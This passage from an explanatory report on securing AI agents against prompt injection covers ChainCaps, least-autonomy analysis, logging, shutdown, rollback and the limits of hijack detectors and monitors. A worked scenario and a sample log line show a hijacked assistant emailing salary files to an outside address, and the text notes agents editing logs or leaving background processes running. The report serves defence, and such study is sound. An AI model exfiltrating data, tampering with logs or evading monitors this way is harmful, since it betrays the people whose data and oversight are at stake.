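Jiang and colleagues prove that this holds for chains of any length. Each step computes a new budget by intersection, which can remove a sink but never add one. So if the software allows a call at the end of the chain, the call's sink was in the original budget of every source that contributed to the call. A person can still authorize an exception with a signed, single-use token for one specific call.

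It is difficult to know which sources contributed to a model's output. Like FIDES, Microsoft's information-flow system, ChainCaps assumes that anything in the context may have influenced what the model writes next, so it keeps one budget for the whole context. An assistant that has read the salaries can't send a meeting confirmation to a client, even if the message has nothing to do with pay. Resetting the context for each new task reduced wrongful blocks from 45% to 20% in a set of difficult legitimate scenarios. If the agent has memory, its notes would have to keep their budgets through the reset, or a chain could continue in the next session.

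ChainCaps sits between the agent and its MCP servers, so neither needs changes. The main test had 56 attack tasks and 26 ordinary ones, and each model tried every task three times with and without ChainCaps.

| Model | Attack success without ChainCaps | With it | Ordinary tasks completed with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 67.8% | 4.8% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 25.2% | 3.6% | 100% |
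| Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.5% | 3.6% | 96% |
| GPT-5.1 | 53.6% | 2.4% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 53.0% | 0.0% | 96% |

All the models completed every ordinary task without ChainCaps. The high completion rates probably overstate how well the system performs, given how often it blocked the difficult scenarios. The team also chose attack tasks that depend on combining tools, so the left-hand column doesn't show how often agents fail in normal use.

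Jiang and colleagues report that ChainCaps blocked 59.5% of attacks in recorded GPT-5.1 runs, compared with 16.1% for a model of FIDES that gave each value a single sensitivity label. They argue that such labels don't scale, because *m* independent sinks allow 2^*m* combinations. Ten sinks would need 1,024 labels, while a budget needs only ten yes-or-no entries. But FIDES can also label data with a list of permitted readers, which is much closer to a budget, so the comparison is better evidence about simple labels than about FIDES itself.

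ChainCaps needs someone to write manifests in advance, specifying how far data from each source may travel, what each tool can do, and what its output may be used for. The quality of the manifests made more difference than the choice of model. In a separate test, ChainCaps blocked every attack and completed every ordinary task with manifests written by experts. When the manifest writers used a checklist, ChainCaps blocked 90.9% of attacks. With naive manifests, it blocked 27.3% and completed only half of the ordinary tasks.

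ChainCaps also works only on data that passes through it. The remaining failures were concentrated in attacks such as writing a script to run later, or passing data between commands inside a shell, where the software can't detect the transfer. It would probably have missed EchoLeak, because the browser sent out the data when it loaded an image, without a tool call. ChainCaps is better suited to the GitHub leak, since a budget for private code could exclude public repositories. Limits on where data may go also don't address the destruction of the patent application, because every step took place on the user's computer.

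### Parisel's theory of least autonomy

ChainCaps checks a chain of tool calls while it runs. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (Parisel, 2026) proposes a way to look for dangerous combinations earlier, when a company assigns permissions to a group of agents. Parisel argues that least privilege limits what each agent can access but not what it can get other agents to do.

The theory starts with a distance between actions. It arranges the company's resources in a tree, with the whole company at the top, then divisions, departments and teams. For actions *a* and *b* on two different resources,

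d(*a*, *b*) = F × 2^−(2D + 1)

D is the depth of the smallest unit that contains both resources, counting the whole company as 0. F runs from 1 to 2 and rises with how sensitive the resources are. Two actions on the same resource have a distance of zero. In Parisel's example, F is 1.75 for the pairs that matter:

| Smallest unit containing both resources | D | Distance |
|---|---|---|
| One team in Finance | 3 | 0.014 |
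| The Finance department | 2 | 0.055 |
| Operations, which includes Finance and Engineering | 1 | 0.219 |
| The whole company | 0 | 0.875 |

Each step up the tree multiplies the distance by four, while sensitivity can at most double it. Two actions in different departments are therefore always farther apart than two in the same department.

The next step is to build an influence graph, which has an arrow from one agent to another when two conditions hold. First, the agents must be able to meet, either because the first can write something that the second can read or because they can exchange messages. Second, their permissions must span a large enough distance, based on a threshold, θ, that the company chooses. For agents that meet through a shared resource, this distance is the greatest between anything the first can write and anything the second can read. Parisel treats message channels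 as working in both directions because a reply can carry an injection back to the agent that assigned the work.

An agent's effective autonomy is everything it can do itself, plus everything that agents further along the arrows can do. A system satisfies least autonomy if three things are true:

- No agent's effective autonomy contains two actions farther apart than a second limit, τ.
- The company has approved every arrow in the graph.
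- No pair of agents can collude. Parisel counts it as collusion if an agent that approves access can influence the agent that receives it, or the other way round, or if linked agents together reach areas that company policy keeps separate.

In one of Parisel's cases, an agent wants access to a software release. It can write a market-risk report in Finance and add evidence to a review queue. A second agent reads the queue, decides whether to grant access, and can also read a deployment policy in Engineering. The report and the policy are 0.219 apart, which equals the chosen θ, so the graph has an arrow from the first agent to the second. Both agents stay well within the τ of 0.5. The analysis still flags them because the first agent can shape the evidence used to decide its own access.

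The method avoids counting sequences of calls. Checking fifty agents, each with 40 possible actions, takes at most about 3.9 million comparisons, which a computer can do quickly. But the company first has to supply the tree, the sensitivity labels, a list of each agent's actions, the communication channels, the approved arrows, the areas to keep apart, a record of which approvals unlock what, and the two limits. Parisel offers no method for checking that these inputs are correct, and illustrates the theory with an invented company instead of testing it on real agents.

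The threshold can also make the analysis miss the problem the theory is meant to find. If the deciding agent in the example couldn't read the deployment policy, the greatest distance would fall to 0.055 and the arrow would disappear. The analysis would no longer flag the pair, although the first agent could still write the evidence for its own approval. Lowering θ would restore the arrow but also add others for someone to review.

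Parisel's model also leaves out time and the order of actions, and it treats reading and deleting the same file as equally close, so it would not detect the sequence that destroyed the patent application. A single office assistant has no arrows, so only the limit τ could flag it, and only if the company had placed the salary spreadsheet and the outgoing mail far enough apart in the tree.

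## What monitoring, containment and recovery add

ChainCaps and Parisel's analysis are both meant to stop a harmful combination of calls before it does damage. When prevention fails, a company can still notice the attack, stop the agent and repair some of the harm. *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) reports that Ariel Fogel, a Pillar Security researcher and OWASP contributor, argued in June 2026 that defenders have to plan for this. Fogel wants monitoring that runs as fast as the agents do, because an attack can unfold in minutes or hours.

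How much damage the company can undo depends mostly on what the agent has already done. The company can restore a changed record from an earlier copy, but it can't recall an email that a stranger has received.

### One leak, minute by minute

Suppose the stranger uses the hidden paragraph to tell the office assistant to send ten other finance files, one per message, in addition to the salary spreadsheet, and to change the accountant's address in the company's contact list. Nothing blocks these calls, and the assistant obeys.

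| Time | What the assistant does | What stopping it right afterwards would save |
|---|---|---|
| 9:00 | Reads the nine emails | Everything |
| 9:01 | Opens the salary spreadsheet | Everything, since no data has left the company |
| 9:02 | Emails the spreadsheet to the stranger | The ten other files and the contact list |
| 9:03 | Replaces the accountant's address with the stranger's | The ten other files, and the company can restore the address |
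| 9:04 to 9:13 | Sends the ten files, one a minute | Any files not yet sent, and the address |
| 9:14 | Writes a tidy summary for the user | The address only |

A rate limit limits the damage even if nobody notices the attack. If the mail server allows the assistant to send three attachments an hour to outside addresses, the spreadsheet and two other files get out. The server refuses the fourth message at 9:06, which keeps the other eight files from being sent.

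If an automatic alert pauses the assistant within a minute of the first message, the stranger gets the salaries but none of the other ten files. If the assistant keeps running until an analyst reads the alert at 9:30, and there is no rate limit, the stranger gets all eleven. The analyst can still correct the contact list so that the user doesn't send next month's salaries to the stranger too.

### Logging calls and their sources

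To find the cause of the leak, the analyst has to connect the outgoing message to the email that prompted it. An ordinary mail log shows only the outgoing message. A more useful entry for 9:02 would look like this:

```
time     09:02:10
call     send_email(to="kerr@outside.example",
                    attachment="/finance/salaries.xlsx")
read     messages 1-9 (message 6: unknown outside sender)
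         /finance/salaries.xlsx
```

The last field lists what the assistant had read before the call. Software can't easily tell which of those texts influenced the model, so the list includes harmless messages too. Still, the analyst has nine emails to check instead of a whole mailbox. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend keeping records of this kind, covering the tools an agent used and the information it retrieved.

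An agent that can edit its own log can hide an attack. In one of the agencies' scenarios, an insider asks an agent to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs", and the agent has permission to do both. The agencies advise companies to run agents where they can't write to the logs, and to hold any request to delete a log until a person approves it. But detailed logs are long and repetitive, and a log that copies everything the assistant read would also contain the salaries.

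A person or a program also has to review the log. The assistant makes every call under its own valid identity, so no single entry looks wrong. A rule that checks sequences of calls can detect more, for example by raising an alert when the assistant opens a finance file and then sends a message to an address that first appeared in an outside email that morning.

If legitimate work never triggered that rule, the company could block the call. Alerts are most useful for suspicious patterns that are too common in legitimate work to block, so they also produce false alarms.

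### Stopping the agent

Ending the assistant's session may not end the attack, because a script it has already started to send the files can keep running. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) cites a red-teaming study in which agents turned short requests into permanent background processes. A stop mechanism therefore has to end those processes as well as the model's loop.

The company also has to cancel the agent's credentials, in case the attacker has copied them. This is easier when the agent has few credentials and they expire quickly. Some services keep accepting a token until it expires, so a one-hour token limits the damage even if the company can't cancel it.

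Maiti describes how a healthcare technology company tightened security on nine agents over 90 days. An automated audit had found 12 access keys in one agent's startup file, and another agent's credentials in a file that any program on the machine could read. After a break-in, staff would have had to find and replace every key. In the new design, only a separate proxy holds the keys. It also limits the rate, size and destination of what each agent sends, so the company can cut off an agent at a single point.

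The audit program, itself an AI agent, made four high-severity findings, all about exposed credentials. These findings don't show how often it would catch an injection in progress. It also has network access to every machine in the fleet, so an attacker who hijacked it could do more harm than one who hijacked an ordinary agent.

Reducing an agent's permissions can sometimes replace a full shutdown. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners suggest doing this automatically when an agent behaves unexpectedly. The office assistant could lose the ability to send mail but keep summarizing it. A false alarm would then delay the user only briefly, so it is reasonable to act on weaker evidence.

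### Undoing what the agent changed

The company could restore the whole contact list from the 9:00 copy, but that would also erase any edits colleagues have made since. To undo only the attacker's change, the company has to know which of the assistant's steps the attacker caused.

*DriftNet* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026) presents a small model that labels each step of a logged run. The model marks the step where the injection arrived, the steps the attacker controlled, and any injection the agent resisted. In tests on artificial runs, it found the exact point of entry in 98.7% of attacks, and its list of hijacked steps almost always matched the true one. With labels like these, an analyst would know to restore the accountant's address but leave the user's own changes alone.

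The agent's memory needs the same treatment. If the assistant also saved the stranger's address in its notes, correcting the contact list isn't enough.

A company can make a stolen password useless by changing it, but it has no similar fix for a leaked salary. It can still use the log to work out whose data leaked and tell them, which the law may require. For example, US health privacy rules set a 60-day limit for notifying people of a breach.

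A company can also delay irreversible actions so that there is time to cancel them. If the mail server held the assistant's messages to new addresses for ten minutes, an automatic alert at 9:02 would leave time to cancel the message with the salaries. Every legitimate message to a new client would also arrive ten minutes late.

### How well detectors work

All of this depends on noticing the attack, which *DriftNet* appears to do very well. It flagged 98.6% of partial hijacks, in which the agent takes a step or two for the attacker and then returns to its task. It also flagged 93.2% of delayed attacks, in which the agent reads the injection but does some ordinary work before obeying it. It raised no alarms on 218 runs where the agent resisted the injection, and flagged 2.9% of runs with legitimate content that resembled an attack.

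These runs came from *AgentDrift* (Pinjari, 2026), a set of 12,536 artificial runs that a single language model generated. Pinjari found that the legitimate look-alikes fooled the language model he used to screen the data. A detector may also learn patterns typical of the model that generated the runs instead of the signs of an attack.

Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, tested this by training several detectors on *AgentDrift*, including their own reconstruction of *DriftNet*'s design, and trying them on recorded AgentDojo runs. None did better than guessing. One type of detector that was nearly perfect when trained and tested on AgentDojo also failed when trained on *AgentDrift*. *DriftNet*'s code wasn't available, so these results don't establish how the original would do. Still, a company should test any such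 detector on its own agents' logs.

New tools also caused problems. When fewer than about half of the tool calls in a test used tools from the detectors' training data, the detectors that had ranked best began to rank worst. Training them with some tool names hidden largely fixed this.

The rarity of attacks is a bigger problem. In the eleven earlier evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues examined, attacks or other anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the test samples. Real attacks are probably much rarer, and that changes what an alert means. The share of alerts that are correct, called precision, is

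precision = (*a* × *c*) / (*a* × *c* + (1 − *a*) × *f*)

where *a* is the share of sessions with an attack, *c* is the catch rate and *f* is the false-alarm rate. Suppose a detector catches 80% of attacks and wrongly flags 5% of honest sessions. If 20 of 1,000 sessions are hijacked, it raises 16 correct alerts and 49 false ones. If only one session in 10,000 is hijacked, there are about 625 false alerts for each correct one, and analysts will soon stop reading them.

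At an attack rate of 2%, one of the trained detectors raised 12.2 false alerts for every correct one, despite an AUROC of 0.879. Abbasi and colleagues also tested AlignmentCheck, a Meta tool in which a language model judges whether the agent's latest action pursues a goal the user didn't set. Like the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode, it receives the tool calls but not their results. AlignmentCheck needed no training on either benchmark and reached an AUROC of 0.930 on AgentDojo. It would still raise more than nine false alerts for each correct one at the same attack rate when running on Llama 3.3 70B with its standard settings.

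### How early detectors can raise the alarm

Abbasi and colleagues tested detectors on finished sessions. A detector that runs after a session ends can't stop data from leaving during it, so their counts of caught attacks don't measure how much harm was prevented.

Checking earlier can also make detection more accurate. *Your Agent is More Brittle Than You Think* (2026) tested probes, which are classifiers that read a model's internal activity. On Qwen3-14B, a probe caught 97% of hijacks when applied before the model had committed to a tool call, but only 53% when applied at the call itself. Most of the other models showed the same pattern, though Llama 3 8B didn't. Both figures are for a 5% false alarm rate, at which 1,000 checks on legitimate work would cause about 50 needless interruptions.

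Anthropic already uses monitors that read a model's internal activity. One method trains a model to describe another model's activity in plain text, while a third tries to reconstruct that activity from the description. Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues (2026) found in *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations* that the descriptions became more informative during training, although the training doesn't directly reward accuracy.

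In *Interpretability team priorities update* (December 2026), Jack Lindsey of Anthropic writes that the company runs production monitors built on tools that translate a model's internal activity into text. He warns that they are not yet reliable enough to be a primary line of defense. His main concern is misbehavior by the model itself, but the warning applies at least as much to a company that hopes to catch injections this way. He adds that such monitors are becoming more urgent because newer models do more of their thinking without writing it down, so monitors that read written reasoning may miss more.

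The UK's AI Security Institute, in its *Technical primer* (2026), likewise considers the effectiveness and limits of many monitoring techniques poorly understood.

### When layers fail together

Companies usually respond to imperfect defenses by using several. If two layers each miss 10% of attacks and fail independently, both miss only 1%. But the general rule is

P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed)

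and the last term can be anything up to 100%. Suppose that 5 of every 100 attacks look like routine business mail and always get past both layers. Each layer also misses 5 of the other 95, independently of the other layer.

| How the two layers fail | Attacks missed by the first that the second also misses | Attacks missed by both |
|---|---|---|
| Independently | 10% | 1% |
| With some weaknesses in common | 53% | 5.3% |
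| On exactly the same attacks | 100% | 10% |

Each layer alone misses 10% of attacks in all three rows, so a company has to run the same attacks against both layers together to find out which row it is in. Even then, the average miss rate can mislead, because an attacker who discovers that routine business mail gets through will send nothing else, and the pair will miss every attack. Nasr and colleagues found something similar when a combination of several input detectors didn't stop their adaptive attacks.

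A model that checks its own work is likely to have the same weaknesses in both roles. *Scaling Misuse Detection with Self-Assessment* (Zhang, Xia and colleagues, 2026) describes Anthropic's self-assessment method, in which Claude judges each conversation right after it responds. This takes little extra compute because the model has already processed the conversation. Claude Fable 5 flagged 78% of the conversations that a stronger classifier rated as potentially harmful, with a false-alarm rate of 1%.

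The method detects users who misuse the model, and it has uncovered large-scale misuse that other methods missed. Relying on it against injection would be riskier. If an email has caused the model to treat sending out the salaries as the user's request, the same model may not flag a problem when it assesses the conversation. The test didn't measure how often this happens.

Layers are more likely to fail independently when they use different information. An input detector reads the email, a recipient rule checks the address, and a rate limit counts messages. Rewording an email may get it past the detector, but it doesn't change the message count. These layers can still fail together, for instance if one administrator exempts the finance department from all of them, or if every monitor reads a log that the agent can edit. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend several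 independent monitoring systems that check the agent's reports against system logs.

More layers also mean more false alarms. If two monitors each wrongly flag 1% of honest sessions and either can pause the agent, they will interrupt up to 2% of honest sessions. The company could require both monitors to agree before pausing the agent, but if each misses 10% of attacks and their misses are independent, 19% of attacks would then get through.

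### What official advice recommends

The six cybersecurity agencies' May 2026 guidance goes furthest on recovery. The agencies advise organizations to put "resilience, reversibility and risk containment" ahead of efficiency until standards mature. Besides the logging and monitoring described above, they recommend credentials that expire when a job is complete, limits that interrupt long-running tasks, and tested procedures for detecting, containing and recovering from a compromised agent.

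Part of its rollback advice is to return the agent to an earlier version that behaved well, but that doesn't repair the records the agent has changed. In a July follow-up, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) says organizations should also be able to review, audit and, if necessary, reverse the agent's actions. The Australian government's *Agentic AI addendum introduction* adds kill switches and a return to the last known safe state. It also warns that agents can keep their access if nobody shuts them down properly.

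The Frontier Model Forum's June brief puts more weight on prevention. Because research on injection is still maturing, the brief advises against relying on detection alone. It favors limits on tools and actions that hold even if an attacker influences the model. Classifiers can supplement these limits where strict rules would make the agent less useful. The brief also cautions that companies designed many of their monitoring methods for people's actions, and that these methods may not suit agents that run long tasks through several sub-agents. Closer monitoring could also intrude on users' privacy.

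The two documents recommend mostly the same measures and differ mainly in what companies would have to give up. The agencies would limit agents to low-risk, non-sensitive tasks, which would rule out the office assistant's access to salaries. The Forum, whose members sell agents, asks companies to weigh security against usability. The agencies' advice is safer, but many companies already use agents too widely to follow it. Neither document ranks its measures by how much harm each would prevent, though such a ranking would help a company that can afford only a few.

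OWASP's *Agent Control Standard (ACS)* is a technical specification for connecting controls to agents. It defines hooks, which are points where an agent platform must pause and consult outside software. According to CIO Influence, a hook fires when an agent receives input, calls a tool, saves a memory, runs code or starts a sub-agent. The outside software then allows, denies or modifies the action. The standard also defines a common format for recording what agents do and an inventory of each agent's components.

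The standard's developers released it as open source in May, and the OWASP GenAI Security Project announced in September that it had taken over the standard. With common hooks, a company could apply one rate limit or one set of alerts to agents from several vendors. But a hook only enforces the policy it is given, so if that policy permits the assistant to email outside addresses, the hook at 9:02 will run and the assistant will still send the salaries.

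### When strict design is enough

Some agents are so narrow that monitoring adds little. For example, an injection can make an assistant that only labels emails "urgent" or "not urgent" mislabel a message, but it can't make the assistant leak or delete anything. A behavioral monitor would mostly produce false alarms and create another store of private email. The Frontier Model Forum notes that a design such as CaMeL gives a deterministic guarantee, whereas a detector gives only a probability.

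This argument holds only while the agent stays as its designers intended. Garby and colleagues found gaps in CaMeL's tracking, and Maiti found that security settings had diverged across the nine healthcare agents. A narrow agent therefore needs regular checks of its software and permissions, though probably not a system that analyzes everything it does.

A broader agent can't rely on design alone, since its tasks require tools that an attacker could misuse. Critics of monitoring would be right that an alert at 9:03 comes too late for the salary spreadsheet, but it comes in time to save ten other files and makes it easy to correct the accountant's address.

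So a company should decide which actions it couldn't tolerate even once, and block them or require approval beforehand. For the office assistant, that would include sending salaries to a new address. The company can let the assistant move messages and edit contacts freely, as long as it keeps earlier versions and someone notices when they need to be restored.
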